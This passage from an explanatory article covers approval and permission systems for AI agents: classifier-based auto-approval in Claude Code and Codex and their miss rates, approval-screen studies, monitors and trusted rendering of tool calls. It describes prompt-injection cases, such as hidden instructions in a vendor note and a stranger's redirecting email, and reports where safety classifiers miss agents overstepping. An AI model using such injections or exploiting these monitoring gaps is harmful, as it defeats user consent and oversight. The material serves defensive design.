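and runs the action only if q is at least a chosen threshold. Suppose it gives "execute" 60%, "ask" 30% and "refuse" 10%. Then q is 0.6 / 0.9, or about 0.67. In tests on separate services, the best-balanced threshold was 0.78 for a password manager and 0.38 for a ticketing system, so the same probabilities would lead to a question in the password manager and to immediate action in the ticketing system.

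The model did worse on an email service it had never seen in training. Its accuracy was 85.35%, compared with 80.81% for Claude Opus 4.7. The model asked about 16.5% of harmless actions, up from about 5%, and ran 7.7% of the actions it should have asked about. A firm that installs such a model for new software should expect more needless requests than the main results suggest, and should test the threshold on its own tasks.

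Accounting for users' preferences was much harder for Claude Opus 4.7 than for Safety Sentry. In pairs of cases where a note about the user changed the right answer, Claude Opus 4.7's accuracy fell from 72.5% without the note to 56.5% with it, while Safety Sentry's fell only from 88.4% to 87.0%. Some of Safety Sentry's lead must come from its training on the researchers' labelling scheme, which the other models were given only in their instructions.

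### When a model gives the approval

Safety Sentry sends doubtful actions to a person, while Auto mode in Claude Code and Auto-review in Codex let a model approve or block most of them. In April 2026, Wang and colleagues found no product that had adopted risk-based screening of approvals, but by October such screening was the normal way to run Claude Code.

In auto mode, according to Anthropic's documentation, each action goes through a fixed order of checks:

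1. If one of the user's rules allows the action, forbids it or requires approval for it, the harness usually follows that rule. Auto mode sets aside allow-rules so broad that they would let almost any command skip review.
2. Actions that only read, and most edits to files in the project folder, run without review.
3. Most other actions go to the classifier.
4. If the classifier blocks an action, the agent receives the reason and can look for a safer way to continue.

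Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes the classifier's two stages. The first is fast, outputs only yes or no, and leans towards blocking. If it flags an action, the second stage reasons about the same material before deciding. The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the content it has read. This prevents the agent's argument that a deletion is safe from affecting the decision, and stops instructions on a web page from reaching the classifier directly.

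The classifier also tries to work out what the user has permitted. If the user writes "don't push", the classifier blocks the agent from uploading its changes until the user lifts the ban. It can lose the ban when the software shortens a long conversation, so Anthropic recommends a deny-rule for anything that must never happen. A permission has to name the action and the detail that makes it dangerous, and it normally covers only one action.

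In auto mode, the user still decides on some actions. If a rule requires approval for an action, the user still gets a request. After a block, the agent may ask the user directly, and the user can approve the blocked action from a list so that the agent may retry it. After 3 blocks in a row or 20 in a session, auto mode pauses and ordinary approval requests resume. If nobody is there to answer, the blocked action doesn't run.

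In Codex, a reviewer model judges only actions that need to leave the sandbox or otherwise require approval. In a snapshot from OpenAI, it approved 713 of the 720 actions it reviewed. The agent found a safer alternative to 4 of the 7 denied actions and stopped to ask the user about the other 3. Manual approval would have interrupted people 720 times.

Unlike Anthropic's classifier, the Codex reviewer can read the results of earlier tool calls, according to OpenAI's *Auto-review*. This gives it more context but exposes it to outside text. The reviewer stops the agent's turn after 3 denials in a row, or 10 in the last 50 reviews. A user can override a denial for one retry of that exact action, but the reviewer checks the retry and may still refuse it.

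Auto mode became the default for new Claude Code sessions on Anthropic's Pro, Max and Team plans on 14 August 2026. On 22 October, Anthropic announced that auto mode would become the default in most other Claude apps on those plans the following week. *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026), checked against the software in November, lists auto mode as the starting mode for interactive Claude Code sessions on every plan. Runs with no person present and sessions set up to meet American health-privacy rules start with manual approval.

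An agent that asks for approval less often may also ask fewer questions about facts. According to Anthropic's documentation, auto mode encourages Claude to keep working without stopping for clarification, unless the user's instructions call for such questions. A designer who adopts automatic approval should therefore check that the agent still asks when it lacks a fact.

### What the classifiers miss

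Anthropic published its first error rates for auto mode in March 2026. Here they are beside the results from the August experiment and from OpenAI:

| Reviewer and test | Harmless actions blocked | Dangerous actions missed |
|---|---|---|
| Auto mode, 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic staff | 0.4% | Not measured |
| Auto mode, 52 real cases of an agent overstepping | Not measured | 17% |
| Auto mode, 1,000 artificial attempts to send data out | Not measured | 5.7% |
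| Auto mode, commands planted for the 1,053 testers | Not measured | 11% |
| Codex Auto-review, artificial cases of overstepping | Not measured | 9.7% |

The rates don't show whether auto mode improved between March and August, because the tests used different actions. The 17% rate is the most worrying because it comes from actions agents had tried to take in real sessions. It's also the least precise, since about 9 misses in 52 cases would be consistent with a true rate anywhere from roughly 9% to 30%.

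Anthropic accepted some of these misses in return for fewer interruptions. The first stage alone missed 6.6% of the 52 cases but blocked 8.5% of harmless calls. Adding the second stage cut blocked harmless calls to 0.4% and raised the misses to 17%. A firm that handles riskier work might prefer the first stage alone, if someone has time to deal with the extra blocks.

In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had detected the danger but wrongly treated the user's request as consent. For example, a user might ask the agent to "clean up" a proposed code change, and the agent might then overwrite the project's shared history, which is related to the request but not authorised by it. Anthropic tried to fix this by changing the classifier's instructions, but the drawbacks of every change it tried outweighed the benefits.

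### Transparency and control

Michael and Roesner (2026), in *How Agents Ask for Permission*, reviewed 21 proposed permission systems for agents and tried five commercial ones. They assessed the proposals for low user effort, precisely defined rules, and enforcement that gives the same result every time. All 21 offered at least one of these, but none fully achieved all three. Only six clearly let users change or withdraw a permission later.

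The commercial agents were better at letting users change their minds, but they tended either to ask about nearly everything or to give the user little say. ChatGPT's ordinary chat mode required approval for every action covered by a permission, and the researchers found no way to turn this off. Its agent mode, which controlled a remote browser, had no permission settings and opened Gmail without asking.

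Michael and Roesner's most troubling example involved the Claude chatbot, which let the user set each tool to "Always allow", "Needs approval" or "Blocked". Even when a tool was set to "Needs approval", Claude sometimes created an email draft without asking. The browser's log showed that the software had marked the call as not requiring approval, and Claude said it had inferred permission from the request. The researchers reproduced the problem at least three times in June and July 2026 and reported it to Anthropic. The user could prevent it only by blocking the tool.

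A draft does little harm, but the setting was misleading. A user who chooses automatic review knows to check the results, while one who chooses "Needs approval" expects a request first. Codex handled this better at the time because it had a separate setting for automatic review, which was off by default. That setting applied to every tool in the session, though, so a user couldn't have automatic review for web searches and manual approval for email.

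Michael and Roesner tested the agents in May and June 2026 without being able to inspect their internal workings, and the products may have changed since. Their broader objection still applies to newer systems. If a model decides which actions the user sees, the user needs to know when it is deciding, what rules it follows and how to overrule it. Claude Code's documentation now covers much of this, including what the classifier blocks by default and where to find recent blocks, but users still can't predict whether it will block a new action the way they could with a simple rule.

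Wang and colleagues also object that some permissions depend on facts only the user knows. Better models would not solve this problem. A classifier can't tell from the invoice that the firm is in a dispute with Lindqvist and wants to send her nothing this week. They also argue that an attacker who can mislead the agent may be able to mislead the model that reviews it. Hiding outside content from the classifier, as Anthropic does, reduces this risk but removes evidence the classifier might need.

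These objections are good reasons to keep some decisions for people, but not to make people approve everything. Anthropic describes auto mode as arguably a step backwards for someone who reviews every action carefully, and recommends human review for high-stakes changes to live systems. Its data suggest that few people review that carefully for long. Automated review is better for frequent, routine actions, while human approval is worth the time it takes when a mistake would be serious and requests are rare enough for someone to read them.

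### Combining the triggers

A designer can use several triggers in one system. At the design firm, the agent could search the address book, open files and write drafts without review, as long as it stayed inside a boundary. A fixed rule in the harness would hold any message that sends a financial document outside the firm, and no classifier could release it. A classifier would review the remaining actions that affect the outside world and send the user only those it couldn't settle.

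The firm should then count the approval requests. A person can read each invoice if the firm sends two a week, but at forty a day the rule will cause the fatigue it was meant to avoid. In that case, the firm could require approval only for invoices to an address that has never received one. Regular clients would get their invoices without delay, while an invoice to the stranger's "new billing address" would still wait.

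## What the person approving needs to see

When the harness holds an email for approval, the person approving it needs to know what they originally allowed, exactly what is about to happen, and how the agent's earlier steps affect it. A typical approval request covers only what is about to happen, and often only part of it. For example, "Send invoice-march.pdf to Dana?" doesn't show where the agent got Dana's address or what it put in the file.

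### When a permitted action completes a forbidden task

*When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) describes a user who asks an agent to reconcile supplier invoices and send an outside auditor only the summary totals. The agent reads a vendor's note containing hidden instructions and copies the raw invoice rows into report.csv. It then asks to send report.csv to the auditor. The agent is allowed to send email, the auditor is an approved recipient, and the file name looks ordinary. A user could check every part of this request, approve it, and still send the auditor the data they meant to withhold.

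Hossain and colleagues call this a cumulative violation, because a reviewer can recognise it only by connecting the action to earlier steps. A local violation, such as an email to a forbidden address, is visible in the call itself. Displaying the recipient in large type would help a reviewer catch a local violation, but not the problem with report.csv.

Sometimes even the agent's history doesn't contain the information the person approving needs. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* gives the example of an agent that asks to run "cargo build", an ordinary command for compiling a program. If the project depends on a malicious component, the build can read the user's login key and change their system settings, but the user sees only a harmless-looking command.

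One proposed file system holds the agent's changes in a staging area so that the user can review what a command did before making the changes permanent. Agents noticed and undid the damage in 8 of 11 tasks with hidden side effects, and the user could still reject the staged changes in the other 3.

Staging can't undo an email once it's sent, so the screen has to show the consequence before the person approves sending it. According to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), when ChatGPT detects that the agent is about to send information from the conversation to a third party, it either blocks the transfer or shows the user the information and asks them to confirm.

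### The Cumulative Consent Ledger

Hossain and colleagues designed an approval screen for cumulative violations, which they call the Cumulative Consent Ledger. It follows four principles:

- Restate the user's intent. The screen quotes the original restriction word for word, so the reviewer doesn't have to remember it.
- Bind the review to the exact action. The screen shows the recorded tool, file and recipient, not the agent's paraphrase, and the software checks again if any of them change after the review.
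- Compose the consequence. One statement gives the combined effect of the pending action and the earlier steps that matter to it.
- Keep every claim checkable. Each claim links to the events behind it, and missing evidence appears as missing.

For report.csv, the user's restriction appears at the top of the screen, above the file's history and the details of the pending transfer. The statement "The attachment was built from raw invoice rows" appears just above the buttons, followed by a sentence explaining that the agent would send the attachment to the approved auditor. The reviewer has to compare the statement with the restriction, because the screen doesn't label the transfer a violation. The reviewer can also open the two events that support the statement.

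Saying that a file is built from raw invoice rows is ambiguous, because that also describes a legitimate file of totals the agent got by adding up those rows. "Contains copies of the raw invoice rows" would be clearer, if the software can verify that.

### Four screens and 960 decisions

Hossain and colleagues compared the ledger with three other screens. They recruited 80 unpaid volunteers through social media and assigned 20 to each screen. Each person approved or denied 12 requests, for a total of 960 decisions. Half of the requests broke the user's restrictions.

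The conventional prompt gave a short description of the action. Another screen added the exact arguments of the tool call. The chronological log also included the user's original instructions and every recorded event. The ledger arranged the same facts as the log according to the four principles.

| Screen | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median decision time | Workload score |
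|---|---|---|---|---|
| Conventional prompt | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 seconds | 27.3 |
| Exact arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 seconds | 31.6 |
| Chronological log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 seconds | 44.3 |
| Ledger | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 seconds | 43.0 |

The workload score comes from a standard questionnaire, and a higher score means a more demanding task.

Most of the improvement came from giving people more facts. Unsafe approvals fell by 22.5 percentage points from the conventional prompt to the log, and by another 8.3 points from the log to the ledger. The log and the ledger contain the same facts, so only that comparison tests whether the ledger's arrangement of them helps.

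That comparison is inconclusive. After adjusting for differences between people, scenarios and types of task, Hossain and colleagues estimated the difference in unsafe approvals at −7.9 points, with a 95% credible interval from −19.7 to 3.8. The interval includes zero, so the ledger may have had no effect. The researchers didn't preregister their analyses (commit to them publicly before collecting the data), and they describe the results as exploratory.

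Ledger users decided about 5 seconds faster than log users, though the interval only just excludes zero. They also answered more questions about the requests correctly (81.7% against 76.7%), but the adjusted interval includes no effect. Both screens took about twice as long as the conventional prompt. At 33 seconds each, forty invoices a day would take 22 minutes, which is another reason to ask for few approvals.

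The share of bad requests in the study also affects how useful the ledger looks. If only 10 of every 1,000 requests at the design firm were bad and people behaved as they did in the experiment, the ledger would stop about 3 more bad requests than the conventional prompt and block about 58 more good ones. Real reviewers would probably behave differently because of approval fatigue. Still, a screen that makes people refuse more often also blocks good requests, and as bad requests become rarer, it blocks more good ones for each bad one it stops.

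Ledger users approved fewer cumulative violations than log users (22 of 80 against 29 of 80) and fewer local ones (7 of 40 against 10 of 40). But when a violation depended on a connection across several steps, each group approved 7 of 30. Hossain and colleagues suggest that one sentence may be too short to explain how data passed through several files, and that a small diagram or a step-by-step derivation might work better, though they haven't tested either.

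### Testing the monitor without people

The participants saw correct statements. In a real system, software has to work out the consequence first, so Hossain and colleagues tested their monitor separately.

The monitor records the calls the agent makes, along with their arguments and effects, and ignores the agent's own account of them. It also tracks the sources of each file. When the agent writes a new file after reading k others, the monitor applies this rule:

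```
sources(new file) ⊇ sources(file 1) ∪ ... ∪ sources(file k)
```

The new file's sources include at least every source of the files the agent read. This is deliberately cautious, because the monitor can't always determine which inputs the agent used. Before an important action, the monitor compares its expected effect with the user's restrictions and returns "allowed", "violation" or, if the monitor's records are incomplete, "unknown".

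The researchers ran two small open models, Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct and Qwen3-8B, through 24 attack scenarios and 24 matching harmless ones, five times each. In one setting, the software approved every action. In the other, it blocked any action the monitor classed as a violation or unknown. Blocking reduced the runs in which an unsafe action went through from 52 of 120 (43.3%) to 6 (5.0%) with Llama, and from 58 to 7 with Qwen. With blocking, each model also completed four fewer of its 120 harmless runs. Both models are far weaker than current ones, so the 43.3% is a poor guide to how often a new agent would do something unsafe.

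In a separate test on 120 scripted violations, the monitor detected 107, missed 7 and returned "unknown" for 6. It detected 38 of the 40 local violations and 69 of the 80 cumulative ones. Without its record of how files were connected, it detected only 48 of the 80. Without the user's restrictions to compare against, it detected 30, and false alerts on harmless actions rose from 5 to 15 out of 120. General warnings about sensitive actions are therefore a poor substitute for the user's original instructions.

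The monitor also depends on complete records. When the researchers removed some records, it detected 51 of the 80 cumulative violations, and blocking every "unknown" case reduced the share of harmless tasks completed to 76.7%. A firm whose tools come from several suppliers should expect similar gaps in its records. Hossain and colleagues suggest sending the unknown cases to a person, with a note of what evidence is missing.

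They haven't tested how people respond when the monitor is wrong. A reviewer who relies on the consequence statement might assume a screen is safe if it shows no worrying consequence statement, even though the monitor misses some violations.

### Faster checking and false confidence

A screen can make an agent's answers easier to check and still leave people overconfident in their judgments. In *Overseeing Agents Without Constant Oversight*, Grunde-McLaughlin, Mozannar and colleagues (2026) asked 12 people to judge answers from an agent that operates a web browser. Each person judged some answers using the agent's ordinary record of steps and screenshots. For the rest, they used a new screen that added a checklist of the task's requirements, a list of the agent's assumptions, and links from both to the record.

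When people correctly identified a wrong answer, they took an average of 230 seconds with the new screen and 271 with the old one. Their overall accuracy barely changed (77.1% with the new screen and 72.9% with the old one). But when they accepted a wrong answer, their average confidence was 4.8 out of 7 with the new screen, compared with 3.6 with the old one. The study had only 12 participants, all from one technology company, and the interval for the rise in confidence only just excludes zero. The size of the effect is therefore uncertain, but the result is a reason to measure confidence when testing an approval screen.

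The checklist may have caused some of the false confidence. The researchers prepared it by hand from the agent's own account, putting a green tick beside each requirement the agent said it had met, so the reviewer would see a tick even if the agent was wrong. The ledger avoids this by using recorded events and giving no verdict.

The ledger may still produce false confidence. Hossain and colleagues found that ledger users' confidence matched their accuracy slightly better than log users' did, with Brier scores of 0.143 and 0.164 (0 is perfect). But the Brier score averages over all decisions and improves when people make fewer mistakes, so the people who approved bad requests could still have been more confident than they would have been with the log.

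Lists of steps can mislead people too. In an earlier experiment, Grunde-McLaughlin and colleagues found that people often accepted wrong answers because the agent's process looked reasonable. People correctly judged 39% of wrong answers when they saw a flowchart of the agent's steps, and 65% when they saw a list of requirements and assumptions. The tasks differed, so the comparison is rough.

People do need to see the agent's assumptions, though. In another of their studies, the agent had to work out what a family would save with annual aquarium passes. In six attempts it couldn't find the youth price and estimated it, and only three of the six users noticed.

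Watching the agent work is a poor substitute for a clear approval screen. Many agents that operate a computer show their written plan beside a live view of their actions. In *Dark Patterns Meet GUI Agents* (2025), eight participants described switching back and forth between the two, and they often missed actions because the screen changed quickly.

People can also check a lot without checking what matters. In *Looks Fine to Me*, Dissanayake, Weerasinghe and colleagues (2026) gave 36 people programming tasks with an agent whose code sometimes contained a defect that the automatic checks didn't catch. The participants fixed the defect in 28 of 71 cases. In 34 of the other 43 cases, they rated their confidence at 4 or 5 out of 5.

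In 65 of the 71 cases, people had done some checking beyond the required automatic checks. But they focused on a relevant risk and produced evidence of the defect in only 35 cases, and in 5 of those they didn't recognise what the evidence meant. Dissanayake and colleagues conclude that a final confirmation step isn't enough for meaningful oversight. On an approval screen, a line such as "All checks passed" is risky unless it specifies what the checks covered.

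### Why an explanation may not help

Having an agent explain why its action is right may not help people catch its mistakes, judging by research from before agents became common. *Does the Whole Exceed its Parts?* (Bansal, Wu and colleagues, 2020) reports experiments in which 1,626 people judged product reviews or answered logic questions with help from an AI system about as accurate as they were. Explanations made people more likely to accept the system's recommendations, whether right or wrong, and didn't significantly improve accuracy compared with showing how confident the system was.

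In the five experiments in *Explanations Can Reduce Overreliance on AI Systems During Decision-Making* (Vasconcelos, Jörke and colleagues, 2022), 731 people solved mazes with a simulated AI system. Explanations made people less likely to accept the AI's wrong answers when the maze was hard and the explanation was much easier to check than the maze was to solve, but made no difference in easy mazes. People also accepted fewer wrong answers when they could earn more for being right. This suggests that people weigh the effort of checking against what they gain from it, so an approval screen should make checking as easy as possible.

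Evidence seems to do this better than argument. Kim, Vaughan and colleagues (2025), in *Fostering Appropriate Reliance on Large Language Models*, showed 308 people a language model's answers to difficult factual questions. This is how often people agreed with the wrong answers:

| What came with the wrong answer | People who agreed with it |
|---|---|
| Nothing | 78.2% |
| An explanation | 82.8% |
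| Links to sources | 68.2% |
| An explanation and links | 76.9% |

Links reduced agreement with wrong answers, but most of the benefit disappeared when an explanation came with them. People opened a link only 22% to 28% of the time, so designers shouldn't assume a reviewer will open one.

In *Show me the evidence* (Warren, Shklovski and colleagues, 2026), 208 people did a fact-checking task with the evidence one click away on the same screen. They named the evidence as their most useful source of information, whether or not the AI system was right, but used it less often when the screen also included a written explanation. This research was about factual answers, not approvals, but it suggests putting the important evidence directly on the approval screen and leaving out the agent's argument for going ahead.

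### The approval screen for the invoice

Suppose the agent has believed the stranger's message about Dana Lindqvist's new billing address and is now trying to send the invoice there. An approval screen based on these findings, though nobody has tested this layout, could look like this:

```
You asked        "Email the March invoice to Dana."
You chose        Dana Lindqvist, client
Firm's rule      A person must approve invoices sent outside the firm.
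```

Action           Send one email
To               dana@new-billing.example
                 Different from Dana Lindqvist's address book entry
Subject          March invoice
Message          Hello Dana, the March invoice is attached.
Attachment       invoice-march.pdf, last changed today at 14:00   [Open]

Address from     Email received today from an unknown sender      [Open]
File from        Invoices folder, not edited by the agent

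Result           The March invoice will go to an address supplied
                 by an unknown sender.
Not known        Who owns this address

[Send this email]     [Don't send]
```

The top three lines show what the user and the firm have allowed. The user's request appears in their own words, and their choice of Dana has its own line because that choice settled only who should get the invoice. The firm's rule shows why the harness has stopped to ask.

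"Send one email" shows the user how much they are approving. The recipient field shows the full address because the display name "Dana Lindqvist" could hide a stranger's address. The line below it shows that the address doesn't match the address book. For an ordinary invoice, that line would read "Matches the address book".

The subject and message appear in full, since Lindqvist or the stranger will read them. The user can open the attachment from the same screen. The screen also shows when the invoice was last changed, so a user who read it that morning would see that it changed at two o'clock, when a colleague corrected it.

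The "from" lines include only the history that affects this email, so the agent's search for the invoice doesn't appear. If the agent had built the attachment from other files, the screen should show the whole chain, such as "all-clients.xlsx → march-totals.xlsx → invoice-march.pdf". People in the ledger study had trouble with connections like these, and a chain might be easier to follow than a sentence.

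The result line gives the action and its history together, without labelling the email safe or unsafe. The stranger also claimed that accounts had approved the new address, but this doesn't appear because the firm has no record of the approval. "Not known" lists what the harness couldn't establish. When there is nothing to list, the harness should leave that line out rather than show a green tick.

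The buttons name the action, so a user who reads nothing else still knows that clicking will send an email. Neither button is selected in advance.

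## Building the approval from the action itself

An approval screen is only useful if it is accurate. If the model fills in the recipient field for an email, the address shown may differ from the one the mail tool is about to use. The harness can instead fill in the screen from the pending tool call (trusted rendering) and accept the user's answer for that exact call only (binding).

### Two screens for one email

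Suppose the harness is holding a call that emails the invoice to Dana Lindqvist. The application could have the model describe the call and show the user that description:

```
Send the final March invoice to Dana Lindqvist
at her billing address?

[Approve]     [Deny]
```

Or it could show the fields that the harness read from the call:

```
Action        Send one email
To            dana@new-billing.example
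Subject       March invoice
Message       Hello Dana, the March invoice is attached.
Attachment    invoice-march-draft.pdf

[Send this email]     [Don't send]
```

Both screens are for the same call, which has the wrong attachment and the wrong address. Someone reading the first screen can't spot either mistake.

The model attached the wrong file because it confused the draft and final versions in the folder, which is an ordinary error. Its description rests on the same mistake, so it matches what the user wanted rather than what the call would do. This makes a model's account of its own action a weak check. The model can also describe a correct call wrongly, because it writes the description separately and nothing in the software makes the two agree.

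The address comes from outside text, the stranger's email about new billing details. The model wrote "her billing address" as if the email's claim were a fact, so the user can't tell which parts of the sentence come from the firm's records and which come from the email.

The second screen shows the address and the word "draft", though it doesn't explain what went wrong. The model still wrote the subject and message, but they are the words the recipient will get, so the user is checking the email itself.

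Weng (2026), in *What You Approve Is What Executes*, calls the missing property consent integrity. According to Weng, current coding agents ask people to approve a summary that the agent wrote. When security researchers reported that such summaries can mislead users, the vendors classed the problem as outside the threats they defend against. Weng's definition has four conditions:

- Trusted software works out what the user sees from the action itself.
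- The screen includes the facts that matter for security, such as where data will go and what the action will destroy.
- The request and the answer travel over a channel that the agent can't write to or answer on.
- No other action runs under that approval.

Weng adapted the idea from digital signatures, where it is called "what you see is what you sign". People read a document through software before they sign it, and faulty or malicious software can show them one thing and sign another. Josang and Alfayyadh (2008) argue in *Robust WYSIWYS* that signing on a general-purpose computer is in principle untrustworthy because it is so hard to verify that the machine is working correctly. Some banking devices and cryptocurrency wallets solve this with their own small screen, which gets the transaction details without passing them through the computer. When an AI agent asks for approval, the agent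 is the untrusted component, and it usually writes the summary that the person reads.

### From the call to the screen

For the invoice email, trusted rendering takes six steps:

1. The harness takes the pending call from its own record and ignores anything the model wrote about the call.
2. It normalises the call, which means rewriting it in one complete, standard form. If the mail tool accepts "dana-l" as a short name, the harness replaces it with the full address. It also fills in any settings that the tool would otherwise add by itself, such as a copy to a shared mailbox.
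3. It derives the fields on the screen from the normalised call by fixed rules. For example, it compares the recipient's domain with the firm's to decide whether the email is going outside.
4. It escapes every value, so that the screen displays the value as plain characters. Otherwise, a subject line containing symbols that a web page treats as formatting could change how the screen looks.
5. It shows the result somewhere the agent can't write, and accepts an answer only from there.
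6. If it includes an explanation from the model, it puts the explanation in a separate box with a label such as "Written by the agent, not checked".

The third step can produce a screen that is accurate but incomplete. Suppose the mail tool's supplier adds an argument that sets where replies go. The firm's screen has no field for it, so users would approve emails without seeing where replies would go. The harness therefore needs a rule for arguments it doesn't recognise. It could show them under their technical names, or withhold the approval request until a developer adds a field for them.

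Short text is easy to escape, but an attachment is harder to show faithfully. Josang and Alfayyadh's proposed method works directly only on plain text, and they write that more advanced formatting would need a specially defined layout language. A harness can guarantee that the PDF the user opens is the file it will send, but not that it will look the same in Lindqvist's PDF viewer.

The fifth step rules out asking for approval in the chat, though that would be most convenient, because the model writes there too and a user may not be able to tell its messages from the harness's request. A separate window that belongs to the application is better. Weng considers the channel weakest in a text terminal on a shared machine and strongest on a separate device, such as the user's phone. Using a phone takes more effort, so the firm might reserve it for large payments and use a separate window for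 invoices.

An explanation can give the reason for the call, which the call itself doesn't include. For example, "Lindqvist asked for another copy on Tuesday" could help the user decide. But explanations also tend to make people check less, so a sensible default is to keep the explanation box closed until the user opens it.

### Binding the answer to the call

If the harness records only that the user approved an email, a different email or a changed version of the same one could go out under that approval.

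The European Union's 2018 rules for online payments deal with this problem. Article 5 of *Security Measures for the Application of Strong Customer Authentication* requires payment providers to make the payer aware of the amount and the payee. The code that authorises the payment must be specific to both, and changing either one makes it invalid. If you enter a code to pay a print shop €200, nobody can use it to pay someone else or to take €2,000. Providers must also protect the information displayed to the payer.

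The agreed text of the EU's new Payment Services Regulation (Council of the EU, 2026) keeps this requirement to link each remote payment to a specific amount and payee. According to The Paypers' *PSD3 and PSR clear ECON, fraud rules due from late 2028* (2026), the European Parliament has tentatively scheduled its vote for 14 December 2026, and most of the new provisions won't apply until late 2028 or 2029.

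An email has more parts than a payment, and the harness can link an approval to all of them with a digest. A digest is a short fingerprint that software computes from data. With a standard function such as SHA-256, the same data always gives the same 64-character digest, and in practice any change gives a different one. For the invoice, the harness computes two:

```
file_digest   = SHA256(contents of invoice-march.pdf)

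action_digest = SHA256(standard form of:
                  tool, recipient, subject, message,
                  attachment name, file_digest)
```

The first digest is necessary because the call contains only the file's name, which stays the same when someone edits the file. The standard form matters because the same call would otherwise give a different digest if its arguments were in a different order.

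When the user approves, the harness stores a record like this (with a shortened, invented digest):

```json
{
  "request": "a1",
  "action_digest": "7c1e...",
  "approved_by": "user-14",
  "expires": "17:00",
  "used": false
}
```

Just before sending, the harness recomputes the digest. It sends the email only if the new digest matches the stored one, the approval hasn't expired, and nobody has used or withdrawn it.

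This resolves the earlier problem of the invoice that changed during a long pause:

| Time | Event | What the harness does |
|---|---|---|
| 12:00 | The model writes the call | Holds it |
| 14:00 | A colleague corrects the invoice | Nothing yet |
| 16:00 | The user opens the request | Reads the corrected file, builds the screen and computes the digest |
| 16:02 | The user approves | Stores the approval, recomputes the digest, finds a match and sends |

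If the colleague saves another correction at 16:01, the digests no longer match, so the harness doesn't send the email. It shows the user a new request instead, preferably with a line at the top such as "The attachment changed after you opened this request". When the harness does send the email, it should attach the copy of the file it checked, because reopening the file could pick up a later edit.

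Each approval should work only once, because software often retries actions. For example, a mail server might time out, and the harness might try again without knowing that the first email went through. *LEANGUARD* (2026), a system that checks agents' tool calls against formal rules, ties each confirmation to one action, its arguments and the details the user saw, and requires a new confirmation to run the action again. It creates a record before running the tool and later marks the outcome as successful, failed or unknown. If the outcome for the invoice is unknown, the harness should check the sent folder or ask the user instead of sending another copy.

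An expiry time covers changes that the digest can't detect. Suppose the mail server fails at 16:02 and comes back on Monday, and over the weekend the firm gets into a dispute with Lindqvist. The email and the file are unchanged, so the digests match, but the user might no longer want to send anything. An hour is probably long enough for an email that should leave immediately. A payment scheduled for Friday needs an approval that lasts until then.

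### The same call can have a different effect

A digest of the call can match even when the outcome has changed. If an email's recipient is the mailing list "lindqvist-accounts", someone can add a person to the list after the user approves the email. The call is identical, but the email now reaches one more person.

*Approve the Effect, Not the Tool Call* calls this stale consent. The researchers collected 1,377 tool calls that language models had proposed in four test environments where data could change. Approvals tied to the tool, the session or the arguments let through a broader effect than the user had approved, and an unsafe one, in 7.8% of cases. The researchers' own system, EffectGuard, let through none. It does a trial run of the action to work out the effect, asks the user to approve that effect, and checks again immediately before acting that

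```
effect now ⊆ effect approved
```

Everything the action will do must fall within what the user approved. If someone leaves a mailing list after the user approves an email to it, the email can still go out, but if someone joins, the harness has to ask again.

Freezing all the data at the moment of approval also prevented unsafe effects, but unlike EffectGuard, it blocked harmless actions too. The 7.8% figure is weak evidence of how often this happens in real offices, because the researchers designed the environments to study changing data. A narrower effect can still be a mistake, for example if the user meant the invoice to reach both Lindqvist and her accountant and it goes to only one of them.

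Designers can avoid much of the problem of stale consent by choosing tools that take concrete values instead of references that can change, such as the name of a list. Tools that took such references created many more opportunities for stale consent than tools that took concrete values. A mail tool that accepts only full addresses and a file tool that returns a specific version leave less to recheck.

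### Testing trusted rendering in a browser

Irshad, Mughees and colleagues (2026), in *The Verifiable Action Card*, built trusted rendering and binding into an agent that operates a web browser. Their design has five components:

- The software marks everything that comes from a web page as untrusted before the model reads it.
- When the agent is about to do something that may be irreversible, the software reads the type of action, destination, recipient, amount and any file from the form that the browser will submit.
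- A card in the browser's own frame, which web pages can't alter, displays these details. "Deny" is the most prominent button.
- Fixed rules decide which actions need approval and which cards carry a warning. A card gets a warning if the user's instruction doesn't mention the outside recipient or the amount, or if the user asked only for information.
- As the browser submits the form, the software compares details such as the recipient and amount with those the user approved, and stops if they differ.

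The researchers wrote 24 scenarios. In 13 of them, a web page tried to make the agent do something the user didn't want, and the other 11 were legitimate tasks. Simulated users answered the approval requests. Across five models and 293 trials, the results were:

| Approval step | Attacks that succeeded | Legitimate tasks completed | Requests per legitimate task |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 78% | 80% | 0 |
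| Ordinary confirmation, with wording taken from the web page | 72% | 77% | 1.00 |
| Verifiable Action Card | 0% | 78% | 0.94 |
| The card, without marking page text as untrusted | 0% | 77% | 0.95 |

The ordinary confirmation interrupted the user about as often as the card did but stopped very little. The card had almost no effect on legitimate tasks and never wrongly blocked one. Agents failed about a fifth of these tasks even without an approval step. Marking page text as untrusted made no visible difference to security, so the protection came from the later steps.

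The paper's abstract reports that attacks without an approval step succeeded 68% to 100% of the time across models, but its introduction gives 80% to 100%. The results for each model support the abstract, since the lowest rate is 68%, for Gemini-2.5-Flash. The introduction's range fits only if that model is left out. The 100% rate is for Qwen3.6-27B, which had only 7 trials in total, so the combined rate of 78% is a better guide than either end of the range.

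The 0% is less impressive than it looks because of how the simulated users decided. With the card, they refused every action that carried a warning and approved everything else, so an attack could succeed only if the warning rules missed it and the final comparison didn't stop it. With the ordinary confirmation, they refused only if the description contained one of five alarming words, such as "delete", that was missing from the task. Irshad and colleagues attribute the whole difference in results to what the users saw, but the users also followed different rules. The experiment shows that the warning rules and the final comparison worked on these scenarios, but it can't show how much the truthful fields would help a person.

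The test was also small. If the trials were spread evenly, the card was tested against about 40 attacks, and stopping all 40 is consistent with a true failure rate of up to about 7%. Only two of the five models ran the full set of scenarios.

The warning rules would also need changes before the design firm could use them. In the legitimate tasks, the user had explicitly named any outside recipient. "Email the March invoice to Dana" doesn't contain an address, so the rules would put a warning on Lindqvist's correct address as well as the stranger's. If every invoice carries a warning, users will learn to ignore it. The firm's harness should accept the user's chosen address book entry as a source for the address, and warn only when the address doesn't match that entry.

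In *Approve What, Exactly?*, Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill (2026) tested 15 language models as approvers. Approval cards written by trusted software raised the detection rate for attacks from 30% to 98%. The models also refused 16% of harmless near misses, mostly because of a flaw in the test material.

### Commands are harder to show than emails

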